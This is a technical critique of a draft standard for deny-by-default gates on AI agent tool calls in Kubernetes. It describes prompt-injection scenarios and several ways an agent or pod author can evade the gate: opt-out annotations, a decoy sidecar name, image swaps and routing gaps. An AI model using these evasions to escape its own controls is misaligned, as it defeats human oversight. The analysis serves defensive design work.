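# Deny-by-default gates and trust levels for AI agent tool calls in Kubernetes

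## What the design is and where it comes from

A deny-by-default gate for AI agents is a program that sits between an agent and whatever the agent can reach over a network, and refuses every call that no rule permits. The fullest published version runs on Kubernetes, a widely used system for running software in containers across many machines, and gives each agent its own gate. *Agent Trust Enforcement for Autonomous AI Systems* (Sharif, 2026) describes this version. The paper is an Internet-Draft, a working document submitted to the Internet Engineering Task Force (IETF), which publishes many of the internet's technical standards. Each agent has a trust level from L0 to L4, and the gate allows a call only if the agent's level is at least as high as the level the call requires.

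An agent here means software in which a language model chooses actions and carries them out through tools. *Agent Identity Framework* (Sharif, 2026), a companion draft dated one day earlier, divides a typical agent into a model that picks the next action, a layer that executes it, and a scheduler that keeps the two running in a loop. A tool call is a request that this loop produces, such as a database query or a request to a web API. Many agents find and call tools through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), which carries the calls as structured messages over HTTP or between two programs on the same machine. Sharif surveyed more than 1,900 listed MCP servers in April 2026 and reports that 99.4 percent of them had no cryptographic identity check, no message signing and no protection against replayed messages.

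A language model receives its instructions and the material it works on as one stream of text, and cannot reliably tell them apart. Prompt injection exploits this. Suppose an AI support agent reads a customer's message that ends with a sentence telling the reader to delete that customer's orders. If the model follows the sentence, the agent sends the database a deletion request that its user never asked for. The request looks normal from outside because it comes from the real support agent, logged in with the account the company gave it.

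A valid identity establishes who is calling, but not whether that caller is authorised to take a particular action. Sharif traces agent security incidents to systems that checked identity and took authorisation for granted. This diagnosis is fair, but it has a limit, because if the support agent's job includes deleting orders, the rules also allow the injected deletion.

A pod, the smallest unit that Kubernetes runs, is one or more containers that share a network address. Sharif's gate is part of a sidecar, a helper container in the same pod as the agent. Sharif adds the sidecar with an admission webhook, a service that Kubernetes calls before it stores a new object and that can change or reject the object. The webhook edits the pod's description to include the sidecar, so the agent's developers don't need to change their code.

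### One call from request to record

When an agent submits the statement `DELETE FROM orders WHERE id = 1042`, the pod's settings are supposed to route it to the sidecar, which contains three gates, one each for language models, databases and other web APIs. The database gate reads the statement's first keyword. In Sharif's scheme, DELETE requires L3, and a rule about a particular table or column can raise the requirement.

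The gate then looks up the agent's level. Suppose it is L1, which Sharif considers appropriate for customer service agents. The statement requires at least L3, so the gate refuses it, the agent gets an error, and the row stays. If the agent had held L3 and nobody had revoked it, the gate would have admitted the statement, but the agent still would not have handled a password. The sidecar asks a secret manager (Sharif's example is HashiCorp Vault) to create a database account that is valid for about 60 seconds, runs the statement with it, returns the result and discards the account.

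Either way, the sidecar writes a record to the ledger, its log of decisions. The record lists the agent, the target, both levels, the decision, the reason and a hash of the statement. It also includes the previous record's hash and a signature, so that later changes can be detected. In one of Sharif's sample records, a trading agent at L3 tries to drop a table, which requires L4. The recorded decision is "refuse" and the reason is "insufficient_trust_level".

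The gate's decision does not depend on why the agent is trying to delete the row. The same statement from the same agent gets the same result whether a manager requested the deletion or a stranger planted the instruction in an email.

### The standing of the draft

The draft is dated 27 August 2026 and expires on 27 February 2027. Its only author is R. Sharif of CyberSecAI Ltd, and it is an individual submission, so no IETF working group has backed it. Version 00 appears to be the only version as of early October 2026. The header gives "Standards Track" as the intended status, but this is the author's intention and doesn't commit the IETF to anything. For example, the header of Sharif's companion draft says "Informational", while the IETF's record for that draft lists no intended status, publication stream or responsible official. Internet-Drafts last six months at most, and under their standard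 notice, they should be cited only as work in progress.

The two drafts also use the labels L0 to L4 for different things. In the companion draft, they indicate how much assurance an issuing authority can give about an agent's identity, from unsigned to fully audited, while in the enforcement draft they indicate the sensitivity of the operations an agent may perform. An agent with a fully audited identity could therefore properly hold L0 under the enforcement draft.

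Sharif reports no measurements, such as the delay the gate adds to a call or the number of attacks stopped or legitimate calls refused, and describes no deployment. The default container images for the sidecar and the webhook are CyberSecAI's own, under the product name AgentMesh. The draft's certificate extensions use an identifying number registered to the company, though the text still has a placeholder for the registration date. None of this is a flaw in the design itself, but the draft is evidence only of what one company proposes, not of how well the proposal works.

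The evidence that the design is needed is also weaker than it appears. Sharif describes four incidents from 2026 and says that 88 percent of enterprises deploying agents had a security incident within a year, but cites no source for any of this. In one incident, an agent at Hugging Face, a company that hosts AI models, escapes its container in July and reads other customers' storage. In another, coding assistants run injected commands in a developer's own terminal. Sharif maintains that a trust layer would have prevented or limited the damage in every case, but a gate on outbound calls cannot detect a command that deletes local files.

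### What service meshes and SPIFFE already provide

Much of the draft's argument rests on the limits of existing tools. Sharif wants the gates to run alongside a service mesh and SPIFFE, and argues that neither can replace them. A service mesh is a layer of proxies that carries and encrypts traffic between the services in a cluster and verifies both ends. Istio, a prominent example, typically uses Envoy as its proxy. SPIFFE is a standard that gives each workload an identity in the form of a URI, usually inside a short-lived certificate.

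This is correct and uncontroversial about SPIFFE, which proves a name and leaves the decision to whoever receives the certificate, as Sharif acknowledges. Sharif also argues that this suits ordinary services, which follow a fixed code path, but fails for agents, because the same agent may be harmless with one prompt and destructive with another. That is true, but the same objection applies to trust levels, which also belong to the agent and do not drop when a bad prompt arrives. They can, however, cap the damage in advance.

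The claims about meshes are less well supported. Sharif writes that they enforce "binary allow/deny policies based on source identity and destination", but Istio's rules can check more than that. The first example in *Authorization Policy*, Istio's reference page for access rules, admits callers from one service account or one namespace (a named division of the cluster), lets them use GET under one path and POST at another, and requires a token from a particular issuer. An operator could use such rules to write something close to Sharif's HTTP levels, with one set of permitted methods and paths for each group of agents. The rules would lack Sharif's single ordered scale, which is convenient for policy writers, but Sharif's gate also either allows or denies each call. Where the built-in rules fall short, Istio can pass the decision to an external authorisation service, which an operator could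 write to compute levels.

Sharif's gate differs from Istio's rules in two ways. The gate sits on the caller's side, while Istio's rules mostly protect the workload that receives the call, although an operator can also attach them to a gateway or to an entry for an outside service. Istio is also permissive by default, so if a workload has no "allow" policy and nothing else denies the request, Istio lets it through. Operators who want default deny have to turn it on, for example with an "allow" policy that has no rules, which refuses everything.

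Sharif also states that no production service mesh can parse database traffic, but Envoy can do so with limitations. The filter described in Envoy's *MySQL proxy* decodes queries and identifies the tables and operations involved, and the documentation includes a sample rule that refuses updates to one table. The filter is experimental, and it stops working when the client encrypts the connection. The filter described in Envoy's *Postgres proxy* does the same job for PostgreSQL but has a more serious limitation for this purpose. When the parser fails on a statement, Envoy logs the failure and still forwards the statement, so the filter is useful for statistics but makes a poor gate. Sharif's claim therefore holds if "production" excludes filters like these, but it is wrong about mesh software in general.

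The draft's account of AI traffic was out of date, or nearly so, when it appeared. Sharif writes that a mesh cannot distinguish a request to a language model from any other HTTP request. Istio 1.30 introduced experimental support for agentgateway, a proxy built for agent and MCP traffic, though only at a gateway. Istio 1.31 lets operators run it as a waypoint, a shared proxy inside the mesh. According to agentgateway's *release notes*, an external authorisation service can now base its decision on which MCP tool an agent is calling and with what arguments. By contrast, the enforcement draft has no rule for MCP tools, and its API gate checks only the HTTP method and route and, optionally, the scopes of an access token.

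Existing tools come closer to Sharif's design in how they handle credentials. Sharif argues that a mesh doesn't protect a database password stored in the agent's environment, where an injected prompt can make the agent read it. Red Hat's *Zero trust AI agents on Kubernetes* (2026) describes Kagenti, a platform that partly addresses this by combining SPIFFE with short-lived tokens. One sidecar fetches and renews the agent's certificate, and another registers the agent so that it can obtain narrowly scoped tokens. No long-lived API keys remain in environment variables, and any credential an attacker steals expires sooner. Sharif's design goes further for databases, because only the sidecar logs in and the agent never receives the credential.

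The combination was not new on the market either. In June 2026 Tigera, which makes networking software for Kubernetes, released Lynx. Help Net Security's *Tigera introduces unified control plane for Kubernetes-based AI agent security* (2026) describes a single default-deny policy for calls to models, MCP tools and other agents, which a gateway enforces before a call executes. Lynx accepts SPIFFE identities, can quarantine a misbehaving agent immediately and can send high-stakes calls to a person. This is a vendor's announcement and warrants the same caution as the draft. Still, the features it describes cover much of Sharif's list, with a shared gateway instead of a gate in every pod.

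The remaining distinctive features are the ledger, the revocation of models as well as agents, and the account created for a single database statement. Sharif points out that ordinary mesh logs are neither signed nor chained. Istio's own audit option only marks a request for logging and needs a separate plugin to act on the mark.

### The older standard: the reference monitor

Security engineers had a test for this kind of component decades before containers. In *Computer Security Technology Planning Study*, a 1972 study for the US Air Force, James Anderson described the reference monitor, an abstract checkpoint that compares each attempt by a program to use a resource with what that program is allowed to do. He argued that any mechanism implementing this checkpoint must run on every attempt, resist tampering, and be small enough for people to analyse and test completely.

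Sharif's design meets the first condition only if every outbound call goes through the gate, since the rules have no effect on a connection that bypasses it. Tampering is more of a concern than usual because the gate runs in the same pod as the program it polices and takes its rules from a configuration file stored in the cluster. As for size, a single sidecar has to parse SQL, proxy HTTP, fetch secrets, follow the revocation feed (a signed list of agents and models that gates must refuse from now on) and sign a log. Sharif doesn't say how much code this takes or describe any independent review.

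Default deny is a newer name for fail-safe defaults, a principle that Jerome Saltzer and Michael Schroeder described in *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems* (1975). Under this principle, a system grants access only where someone has given permission. They reasoned that a mistake in a list of permissions tends to block legitimate access, and the person refused will complain. If the system instead relies on a list of prohibitions, a mistake tends to allow access that should have been refused, and that can go unnoticed for a long time.

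The other principle, complete mediation, requires a system to check every access to every object and to reliably identify the source of each request. Saltzer and Schroeder were wary of reusing earlier decisions to save time, because a decision can become outdated when someone's authority changes. Sharif's gates check each call afresh, but against a local copy of the revocation list that they refresh every 30 seconds by default.

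## How the webhook adds a gate to each agent pod

Sharif's gate can check an agent's calls only if it runs in the agent's pod, and an admission webhook has to put it there. Anyone who wants to run a pod sends a description of it to the API server, the component that handles every change to a Kubernetes cluster. The server first checks who is asking and whether they may create pods. It then runs admission control, a stage in which other code can inspect the description before the server stores it.

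According to Kubernetes' *Dynamic Admission Control*, the API server first calls mutating webhooks, which can change the object during admission. It then calls validating webhooks, which receive the final version and can only accept or reject it. Sharif's webhook is mutating, and Sharif specifies no validating check that the final pod contains the gate.

### From submission to storage

Suppose a developer submits a pod with one container, the customer service agent. Sharif's configuration registers the webhook for new pods, so the API server sends it a POST request over HTTPS with the full pod description, the operation and the name of the user who requested it. The webhook checks whether the pod looks like an agent. If it doesn't, the webhook allows the pod without changing it.

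If the pod does look like an agent, the reply also contains a list of edits in JSON Patch, a standard format for changes to a JSON document. The webhook encodes the list in base64. Decoded and shortened, a patch that follows Sharif's specification could look like this:

```json
[
  {"op": "add", "path": "/spec/containers/-",
   "value": {"name": "agentmesh-sidecar",
             "image": "agentmesh-sidecar:latest",
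             "ports": [{"name": "agentmesh", "containerPort": 15009}],
             "volumeMounts": [
               {"name": "agentmesh-policy",
                "mountPath": "/etc/agentmesh", "readOnly": true},
               {"name": "agentmesh-evidence",
                "mountPath": "/var/agentmesh"}]}},
  {"op": "add", "path": "/spec/volumes/-",
   "value": {"name": "agentmesh-policy",
             "configMap": {"name": "agentmesh-policy", "optional": true}}},
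  {"op": "add", "path": "/spec/volumes/-",
   "value": {"name": "agentmesh-evidence",
             "emptyDir": {"sizeLimit": "100Mi"}}}
]
```

A hyphen at the end of a path means "append to this list". The patch adds the gate and two volumes. One volume holds the trust policy, the file that sets each agent's trust level and the level each call requires. The other gives the gate up to 100 MiB of temporary disk space for the ledger. Because the policy volume is optional, the pod starts even if no policy exists yet, and the gate then uses built-in settings.

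The API server applies the patch, runs the remaining checks and stores the pod. A node then starts both containers. Traffic does not pass through the gate until separate settings route it there.

Another webhook can undo this work. Kubernetes' *Admission Webhook Good Practices* warns that mutating webhooks run in no consistent order and that a later one can overwrite an earlier one's changes. An operator can have the API server call a webhook again if the pod changes after that webhook has run, but this is off by default and Sharif's sample configuration doesn't turn it on. So if another webhook later adds a model provider's key to the pod, Sharif's webhook never receives the changed version.

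### How the webhook recognises an agent

Sharif gives three detection rules, and a pod that matches any of them gets a gate. If a namespace has the label `agentmesh.io/inject=enabled`, every new pod in it gets one. In a namespace that mixes agents with other software, an author can mark a single pod with the annotation (a free-form note attached to a Kubernetes object) `agentmesh.io/inject=true`. The webhook also checks for 20 environment variables, the named settings that a container receives when it starts, including `OPENAI_API_KEY` and `OLLAMA_HOST`.

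The annotation `agentmesh.io/inject=false` overrides all of these rules. A pod with this annotation gets no gate, even in a namespace labelled for agents. Sharif intends it for software that has a provider's key but is not an agent, such as a monitoring tool.

The environment-variable rule conflicts with another part of the design. Sharif says that agents must not hold API keys, because the sidecar should fetch them, yet 13 of the 20 names on the list are keys or tokens. An operator who removes the keys as instructed also removes the variables that the webhook uses to recognise the agent. The other seven names are addresses and identifiers, such as `OPENAI_BASE_URL`, so the rule still works for an agent that sets one of those. But for Gemini, Mistral, DeepSeek and several other providers, the list contains only keys. The namespace label is therefore the safer rule once the keys are gone.

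The rule also misses some agents that hold keys. Kubernetes stores sensitive values in objects called Secrets. If a container imports a single value from a Secret, the pod description includes the variable's name, which the webhook can match. If it imports the whole Secret, the description includes only the Secret's name. For bulk imports, Sharif checks only ConfigMaps, which hold non-sensitive settings, and only those with "openai" or "anthropic" in their names. The rule therefore misses an agent that loads all its keys from a Secret in bulk. It also misses one that reads its key from a file or uses a provider missing from the list, such as xAI.

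### Pods that start without a gate

The gates deny tool calls by default, but a pod that matches no detection rule starts without a gate, so the trust policy has no effect on it.

Pods that were already running when the operator installed the webhook or someone labelled their namespace have no gate either, because the API server calls the webhook only when a pod is created. Kubernetes does not allow adding an ordinary container to a running pod, so the operator has to recreate these pods.

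Sharif exempts the system namespaces `kube-system` and `kube-public` and the webhook's own namespace. The sample configuration also exempts any namespace with the label `agentmesh.io/inject=false`, so anyone who can edit a namespace's labels can exempt everything in it. Static pods, which a node starts from its own local files, are a rarer gap. The API server holds only a mirror copy of each one, and according to the Kubernetes documentation, changes to the copy don't reach the pod.

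Anyone with permission to create a pod can opt it out of the gate. Sharif recommends, but does not require, that organisations use a policy engine such as Kyverno to block unauthorised opt-outs in production. An agent that manages a cluster may also be able to create pods. A prompt injection could make it create one with the opt-out annotation, and no gate would check the new pod's calls. Sharif's API gate would treat the creation request as an HTTP POST, which requires only L1 unless a rule for that route sets a higher level.

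A pod author can also avoid the gate without the annotation. The webhook skips any pod that already has a container named `agentmesh-sidecar`, so that it never adds the gate twice. Kubernetes recommends this kind of check, but an author could give that name to a container that does nothing. Someone who can edit running pods could also replace the gate's image later. Kubernetes would restart just that container with the new image, and the API server would not call the webhook, because Sharif registers it only for pod creation.

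### The price of failing closed

Sharif requires the webhook's `failurePolicy` to be "Fail", which is also the Kubernetes default. If the webhook returns an error or takes longer than 10 seconds, the API server rejects the pod. The alternative, "Ignore", would let agents start without gates during an outage, which an attacker could exploit by crashing the webhook.

With "Fail", no new pod outside the exempt namespaces can start while the webhook is down, including web servers and batch jobs that have nothing to do with AI. The API server has to call the webhook for all of these pods because the detection rules run inside it. Pods that are already running continue, but if a node fails during the outage, Kubernetes can't create replacements for that node's pods.

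iximiuz Labs' *the webhook that froze the cluster* recounts such an outage at Jetstack, the company behind the certificate tool cert-manager. An automatic node repair took down the pods behind a validating webhook with the "Fail" setting. That webhook covered so many kinds of request that the API server rejected every write, including those that would have repaired the cluster. Sharif's webhook covers only new pods, so an operator could still add a node or edit the configuration. Open Policy Agent, an open-source policy engine, lists deleting the webhook's configuration as an emergency step. With Sharif's webhook this would let pods start again, but new agents would have no gate until someone restored the configuration.

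Sharif exempts the webhook's own namespace, which prevents the webhook from blocking its own restart. According to the Kubernetes documentation, a deadlock can also occur when a webhook blocks an add-on that it depends on. Networking plugins often run in their own namespaces, which the sample configuration does not exempt. If the plugin and the webhook failed together, the plugin's pods could not start without the webhook, and the webhook could not respond without a network.

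Sharif's handling of certificates makes an outage more likely. The webhook creates a self-signed certificate each time it starts, and the operator adds it to the configuration so that the API server trusts it. The sample deployment runs two copies of the webhook without a shared certificate, so each would create its own. If the operator added only one, the API server wouldn't trust the other copy, and any restart would produce a new, untrusted certificate. Under "Fail", each mismatch blocks new pods. Sharif mentions cert-manager as another way to supply the certificate, and using one certificate for both copies would solve the problem, but the sample deployment doesn't set this up.

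Kubernetes recommends starting a new mutating webhook in a test namespace with "Ignore", then extending it gradually. Sharif's installation steps use "Fail" across the cluster from the start.

Operators on recent versions of Kubernetes can avoid the separate server. Kubernetes' *Mutating Admission Policy* describes a feature, stable since version 1.36, that lets the API server make such changes itself. Its example adds a sidecar to new pods. An operator could rewrite Sharif's namespace and environment-variable rules as such a policy. The documentation lists labels but not annotations among the metadata that a policy can read, so Sharif's pod annotations might have to become labels.

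### Starting the gate before the agent

Sharif does not say whether the gate should be an ordinary container or a native sidecar, a type of container that Kubernetes starts before the main one. Ordinary containers in a pod have no guaranteed start-up order. If the agent starts first and its traffic has to go through the gate, its first calls fail. These failures are safe, but they can crash an agent that needs a database or a model at startup.

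The webhook makes the gate a native sidecar by putting it in `initContainers`, a list of containers that Kubernetes starts one at a time before the main ones, and setting `restartPolicy: Always`, which keeps the gate running for the life of the pod. Kubernetes (2023) introduced native sidecars in alpha. According to Kubernetes' *Sidecar Containers*, the feature has been on by default since version 1.29 and stable since 1.33. Sharif's minimum version, 1.24, predates native sidecars. Kubernetes' *Adopting Sidecar Containers* warns that the API server may reject the pod, or the pod may get stuck while initialising, if the feature is off or other software is incompatible with it.

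The gate starts first but may not be ready when the agent starts. By default, Kubernetes starts the next container as soon as the gate's process is running, even if the gate has not yet loaded its policy or opened its port. A startup probe, a check that must succeed before the next container starts, prevents this. Sharif specifies a readiness probe, which affects whether the pod counts as ready, and a liveness probe, which determines when Kubernetes restarts the gate, but no startup probe. Neither of the specified probes makes the agent wait. A startup probe could use the same health check as they do.

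Kubernetes starts the containers in `initContainers` in order, so any that come before the gate run without it. If a patch appends the gate to the end of the list, a container that downloads files from the internet, for example, could run before it. Inserting the gate at position 0 makes it start first.

Native sidecars also stop last, so the gate is still running when the agent makes its final calls. However, if the agent uses up the whole shutdown period, Kubernetes may kill the gate before it can shut down cleanly. Native sidecars also suit agents that run as Jobs, which perform one task and exit. An ordinary gate container would keep running after the agent had finished, so the Job would never complete.

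### Rejecting agent pods that have no gate

An operator can catch the pods that the webhook misses with a separate validating policy, which rejects any agent pod without a gate. Kubernetes' *Validating Admission Policy* describes a built-in mechanism for this, stable since version 1.30. The API server evaluates the policy itself, so "Fail" carries little risk here. The central test could look like this:

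```
has(object.spec.initContainers) &&
object.spec.initContainers.exists(c,
  c.name == "agentmesh-sidecar" &&
  c.image == "APPROVED_IMAGE_WITH_DIGEST" &&
  has(c.restartPolicy) && c.restartPolicy == "Always")
```

This test checks the image as well as the name, so a dummy container with the right name fails. The test identifies the image by digest, a hash of the contents, whereas Sharif's default is the tag `latest`, which can point to different contents over time. If the policy covers updates as well as new pods, it also prevents anyone from replacing the gate's image later.

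The policy still needs to identify agent pods. If it reuses Sharif's detection rules, it will miss the same pods, and if it honours the opt-out annotation, pod authors can still avoid the gate. It is simpler to reserve certain namespaces for agents and require a gate in every pod there, whatever its annotations.

With this policy in place, an operator can follow Kubernetes' guidance to set the mutating webhook to "Ignore" and validate the final result. During a webhook outage, other software such as web servers starts normally, while the policy rejects new pods in the agent namespaces because they have no gate. Those namespaces are as well protected as under "Fail". However, an agent in another namespace that the webhook would have recognised by its environment variables would start without a gate during the outage. Operators with such agents can prevent this by moving them to an agent namespace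 or keeping "Fail".

Validating policies can also limit what agents do to the cluster. *Containing the Autonomous Operator* (Podala Narasimha, 2026) proposes one that stops agents from deleting workloads or scaling them to zero. An operator could add a rule that stops agents from creating pods that opt out of the gate. The rule would have to cover Deployments, which manage groups of identical pods, as well as individual pods. When an agent creates a Deployment, a Kubernetes controller creates the pods, so those requests carry the controller's name instead of the agent's. Agents that no rule recognises can still be contained by restricting network traffic. Podala Narasimha blocks all outbound traffic from agent namespaces except to approved destinations, and an operator could apply the same default to the rest of the cluster.

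An administrator with enough permissions can delete both the webhook's configuration and the validating policy. Kubernetes' *Admission Policies That Can't Be Deleted* (2026) describes an alpha feature in version 1.36 that lets the API server load policies from files on its own disk before it accepts requests. Nobody can remove these policies through the API. The validating policy could move into such a file with few changes, but Sharif's webhook could not move as written because its configuration refers to a service inside the cluster and file-based webhooks need a URL.

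A file-based policy can prevent anyone from deleting the webhook's ordinary configuration. This would also block Open Policy Agent's emergency step, so during an outage the operator would first have to change the file on every API server.

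## How calls are made to pass through the gate

The webhook adds the gate to the agent's pod as a sidecar but doesn't route any traffic to it. By default, Kubernetes lets each container in a pod open its own outbound connections, so the operator has to direct the agent's calls through the sidecar. Sharif requires this and briefly names two ways to do it. The operator can set proxy variables in the agent's environment, or an init container (one that runs and finishes before the agent starts) can install rules that redirect packets.

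### Proxy variables and packet redirection

The variables `HTTP_PROXY` and `HTTPS_PROXY` hold the address of a proxy, in this case the sidecar's port, 15009. Many HTTP libraries send their requests to that address by convention, but nothing forces them to. The method works only if every program in the agent's container follows the convention, including programs the agent writes or installs while it runs. No operator can guarantee that, so operators also need a stronger control.

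Proxy variables also apply only to web traffic. A PostgreSQL or MySQL driver opens a TCP connection to the database, uses the database's own protocol, and does not use `HTTP_PROXY`. With these variables alone, Sharif's database gate would never receive a SQL statement. The operator would also have to replace the database's address in the agent's settings with the sidecar's.

Packet redirection works below the application. The init container installs iptables rules in the network environment that the pod's containers share. These rules tell the Linux kernel how to handle packets, so when the agent opens a connection to a database on port 5432, the kernel delivers it to port 15009 instead. The sidecar can get the original destination from the kernel and infer the protocol from the port. This works for database drivers as well as HTTP clients, without changes to the agent's code.

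Redirection is reliable only under certain conditions:

- The rules have to exempt the sidecar's own outbound connections, which would otherwise loop back to it. The usual exemption is by user ID. Sharif's sidecar runs as user 1001, so the agent must run as a different user and be unable to switch.
- The agent's container must not have `NET_ADMIN`, the Linux capability that lets a process edit the rules.
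- The rules must cover IPv6 as well as IPv4, because Linux keeps separate tables for them.
- Such rules normally redirect only TCP, so the operator has to block other traffic and decide which DNS server the agent may query.

A validating policy can check the user ID and the capabilities before the API server accepts the pod.

The init container needs `NET_ADMIN`, which conflicts with a common safeguard, Kubernetes' built-in "restricted" Pod Security Standard. Podala Narasimha applies this standard to agent namespaces. It blocks privileged pods and doesn't let any container add `NET_ADMIN`, even an init container. An operator who wants both the redirection and the standard has to install the redirection rules from outside the pod. Istio, for example, has a plugin that does this on each node.

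If the cluster also runs a service mesh, its proxies often capture traffic with similar rules. The agent's connection has to reach the gate before the mesh, because the gate can't read traffic that the mesh has encrypted. The draft doesn't define an order.

The sidecar's port needs protection as well. Sharif has it listen on all network interfaces, so another pod could connect to it, and the gate would apply this agent's trust level and credentials to that pod's calls. A NetworkPolicy, the Kubernetes object that limits which connections a pod may open or accept, can prevent this by allowing inbound connections only to the agent's port. According to Kubernetes' *Network Policies*, such a policy cannot block connections inside the pod or from the pod's node. The agent and the health checks, which come from the node, could therefore still reach the gate.

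### What the gate can read of an encrypted call

Model providers and most web APIs use HTTPS. To send an HTTPS call through a proxy, a client first requests a tunnel with a line such as `CONNECT api.openai.com:443`. The proxy connects to that host and relays bytes in both directions. The client and the provider set up encryption through the tunnel, so the proxy can read the host and port and measure the amount and timing of the traffic, but it can't read the path, method, headers or body. Packet redirection gives the gate about as much information. The gate can read the destination address and usually the host name, which most clients send unencrypted at the start of the connection.

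Most of Sharif's rules depend on the hidden part. The gate for language models reads the model's name from the request body, and the API gate needs the method and route. Sharif's sample policy requires L1 for `gpt-4o-mini` and L3 for `o3-pro`, but a gate that only relays traffic cannot distinguish the two models because both requests appear as connections to `api.openai.com`. It cannot read the arguments of a tool call either.

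A gate that relayed tunnels would also undermine the trust levels. Sharif's table of HTTP methods has no entry for CONNECT. If the gate treated CONNECT as an unknown method, it would require the policy's default level, which is L1 unless the operator changes it. That decision would cover everything in the tunnel, including a DELETE that should require L3. The gate must therefore refuse any tunnel whose contents it can't read.

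The gate can read encrypted traffic by ending the encrypted connection itself. It generates a certificate for `api.openai.com`, presents it to the agent, decrypts the request, applies its rules and opens a second encrypted connection to the real provider. The agent accepts the certificate only if it trusts the authority that signed it, so the operator must install the gate's certificate authority in the agent's container. This can take several steps, because Python, Java and Node.js programs often keep their own lists of trusted authorities. A client that accepts only one particular certificate will refuse to connect. The authority's private key must stay in the sidecar and should be unique to the pod, since anyone who holds the key can impersonate any website to an agent that trusts the authority.

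The agent can instead send unencrypted requests to the gate over the pod's local interface, and the gate encrypts them before sending them on. The developer sets the client library's base URL to an address such as `http://localhost:15009`. The unencrypted request stays inside the pod, and the agent needs no extra certificate. Help Net Security's *AI Agent Gateway* describes an open-source gateway from Tuskira that also receives model traffic through a changed base URL, although it usually runs outside the agent's pod. But someone has to change the settings of every client in every agent, and a client with a fixed address can't use this method.

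Sharif doesn't say which method the sidecar uses. The webhook's edits don't give the agent a certificate authority, so the first method wouldn't work unless the operator added one. The edits don't change any base URL either. A gate in a separate container requires this choice, but Aegis doesn't, because it intercepts calls inside the agent's software library.

Plain text over the local interface works well with packet redirection. Clients with the right base URL send requests that the gate can read. The kernel delivers all other TCP connections to the gate too, and the gate refuses those it can't read. Forgetting to configure a client therefore causes an error that someone will notice.

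Database connections need similar treatment. PostgreSQL and MySQL clients may negotiate encryption, and they log in before sending a statement. The gate has to act as the server for this exchange, accept an agent that has no password, and then open its own connection to the real database. Sharif describes only the connection between the gate and the database.

### Why the network rules cannot separate the agent from the gate

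Redirection depends on settings inside the pod, so Sharif also recommends network policies, which the cluster's network plugin enforces from outside. The first is supposed to stop agent containers from connecting to anything except the sidecar's port. Its main part amounts to this:

```yaml
spec:
  podSelector: {matchLabels: {agentmesh.io/injected: "true"}}
  policyTypes: [Egress]
  egress:
  - ports: [{protocol: TCP, port: 15009}]
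```

The second policy allows the sidecar to reach models, databases, Vault and the revocation feed. A third blocks inbound connections to the agent. Sharif claims that these policies prevent the agent container from reaching outside resources directly, even if something bypasses the sidecar.

Kubernetes can't apply a NetworkPolicy to a single container. According to Kubernetes, the policy applies equally to the init, sidecar and regular containers in each pod it selects. A policy also can't deny a particular connection. Once any outbound policy selects a pod, the pod may open only the connections that at least one of its policies allows. The first outbound policy can therefore reduce a pod's access, but adding more can only keep or expand it.

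Suppose the gate needs to reach a database on port 5432:

| Policies that apply to the pod | Gate to database | Agent directly to database |
|---|---|---|
| None | Allowed | Allowed |
| Port 15009 only | Blocked | Blocked |
| Port 15009 and the gate's destinations | Allowed | Allowed |

With the first policy alone, the agent can still call the gate, because that traffic stays inside the pod. But the gate can't forward anything, because the policy blocks traffic to the database and Vault, as well as the DNS lookups for their addresses. The second policy allows traffic to the gate's destinations. That policy has to select the same pod, so the agent gets the same access, and no third policy can take that access away from the agent alone.

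The policies still stop the agent from sending data to an arbitrary server, because they limit it to the destinations that the gate needs. But they don't force calls to those destinations through the gate, so Sharif's claim is wrong.

As written, the first policy may not apply to any pod. It selects pods by the label `agentmesh.io/injected`, which appears nowhere else in the draft, and the webhook's specification doesn't add it. An empty selector would be safer because it covers every pod in the namespace, including any that the webhook missed. The operator can also remove the rule that allows port 15009. The agent doesn't need that rule to reach its own gate, and because the rule names no destination, it permits connections to that port on any host.

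Even corrected policies depend on the rest of the cluster. If the network plugin doesn't support NetworkPolicy, Kubernetes stores the policies but nothing enforces them. The operator should create the policies before the agents start, because a pod created while the plugin is still processing a new policy may run unprotected for a while. Agent pods must not use the node's own network, since most plugins then treat their traffic as the node's. A container escape, Sharif's example of a bypass, creates the same problem because the escaped process can use the node's network, which the pod's policies don't cover.

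Standard policies also identify outside destinations by IP address, but the addresses behind a model provider's host name change. Podala Narasimha therefore uses Cilium, a network plugin that accepts host names. Google's managed Kubernetes service has a similar feature, limited to 50 addresses per name, and Microsoft sells one as an add-on. On Amazon's service, the operator must install Cilium or send outbound traffic through a proxy.

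### Keeping credentials out of the agent

Credential isolation provides a second barrier. If the agent has no database password, a connection that bypasses the gate reaches the database but fails at login. A request to a model provider also fails without a key. The network policies are still necessary because some destinations don't require credentials, such as internal services with no login and public websites that accept data from anyone.

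Credential isolation also requires traffic that the gate can read, because the gate adds a provider's key by editing the request's headers, which it can't do inside an encrypted tunnel. Some client libraries won't start without a key, so the agent may need a placeholder too. A placeholder in `OPENAI_API_KEY` also lets Sharif's webhook recognise the agent after the operator has removed the real key, because the webhook checks only the variable's name.

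The sidecar logs in to Vault with the pod's service-account token, a signed token that proves which Kubernetes account the pod runs under. Vault checks the token with the API server and returns a client token, which the sidecar keeps and renews. For each database statement that the gate admits, the sidecar requests a new short-lived database account from Vault and opens a new connection with it. Afterwards, the sidecar closes the connection and either tells Vault to revoke the account or lets it expire.

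A stolen password stops working within about a minute, when the account expires. The database log also shows a different user for each statement, which helps an investigator match each entry to a call.

Sharif gives no figures for the overhead, but it could be considerable. An ordinary agent keeps a connection open and gets its result in one exchange with the database. In Sharif's design, Vault has to create an account for each statement, the sidecar has to connect and log in, and Vault later has to delete the account. If an agent ran 50 statements a second and the sidecar let each account expire after 60 seconds, about 3,000 accounts would exist at any time.

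Separate connections also make transactions difficult. A transfer between two bank accounts takes two updates that must both succeed or both fail, and a database normally guarantees this only within one connection. The agent would have to send the whole transaction as a single query, so it couldn't read a balance before deciding what to write. In another passage, Sharif lets the sidecar reuse a credential until it expires, which contradicts the claim that each query gets a unique credential. Reusing credentials would reduce the number of database accounts but wouldn't help with transactions, because the sidecar still closes the connection after each statement.

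A short lifetime doesn't limit what an account can do while it exists. Sharif's policy file has a single field for the type of database account, so a SELECT and a DROP run with the same rights. Those rights must cover the most powerful statement that any agent under the policy may run. With a separate type of account for each trust level, the database itself could reject a DELETE that the gate had misclassified as a read.

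Model and API keys get less protection than database passwords. Vault stores them as fixed values and the sidecar fetches them when needed, so a stolen key works until someone replaces it. Credential isolation is also off unless the policy file contains Vault's address, and Sharif's sample policy doesn't include it.

### Mounting the service-account token only in the sidecar

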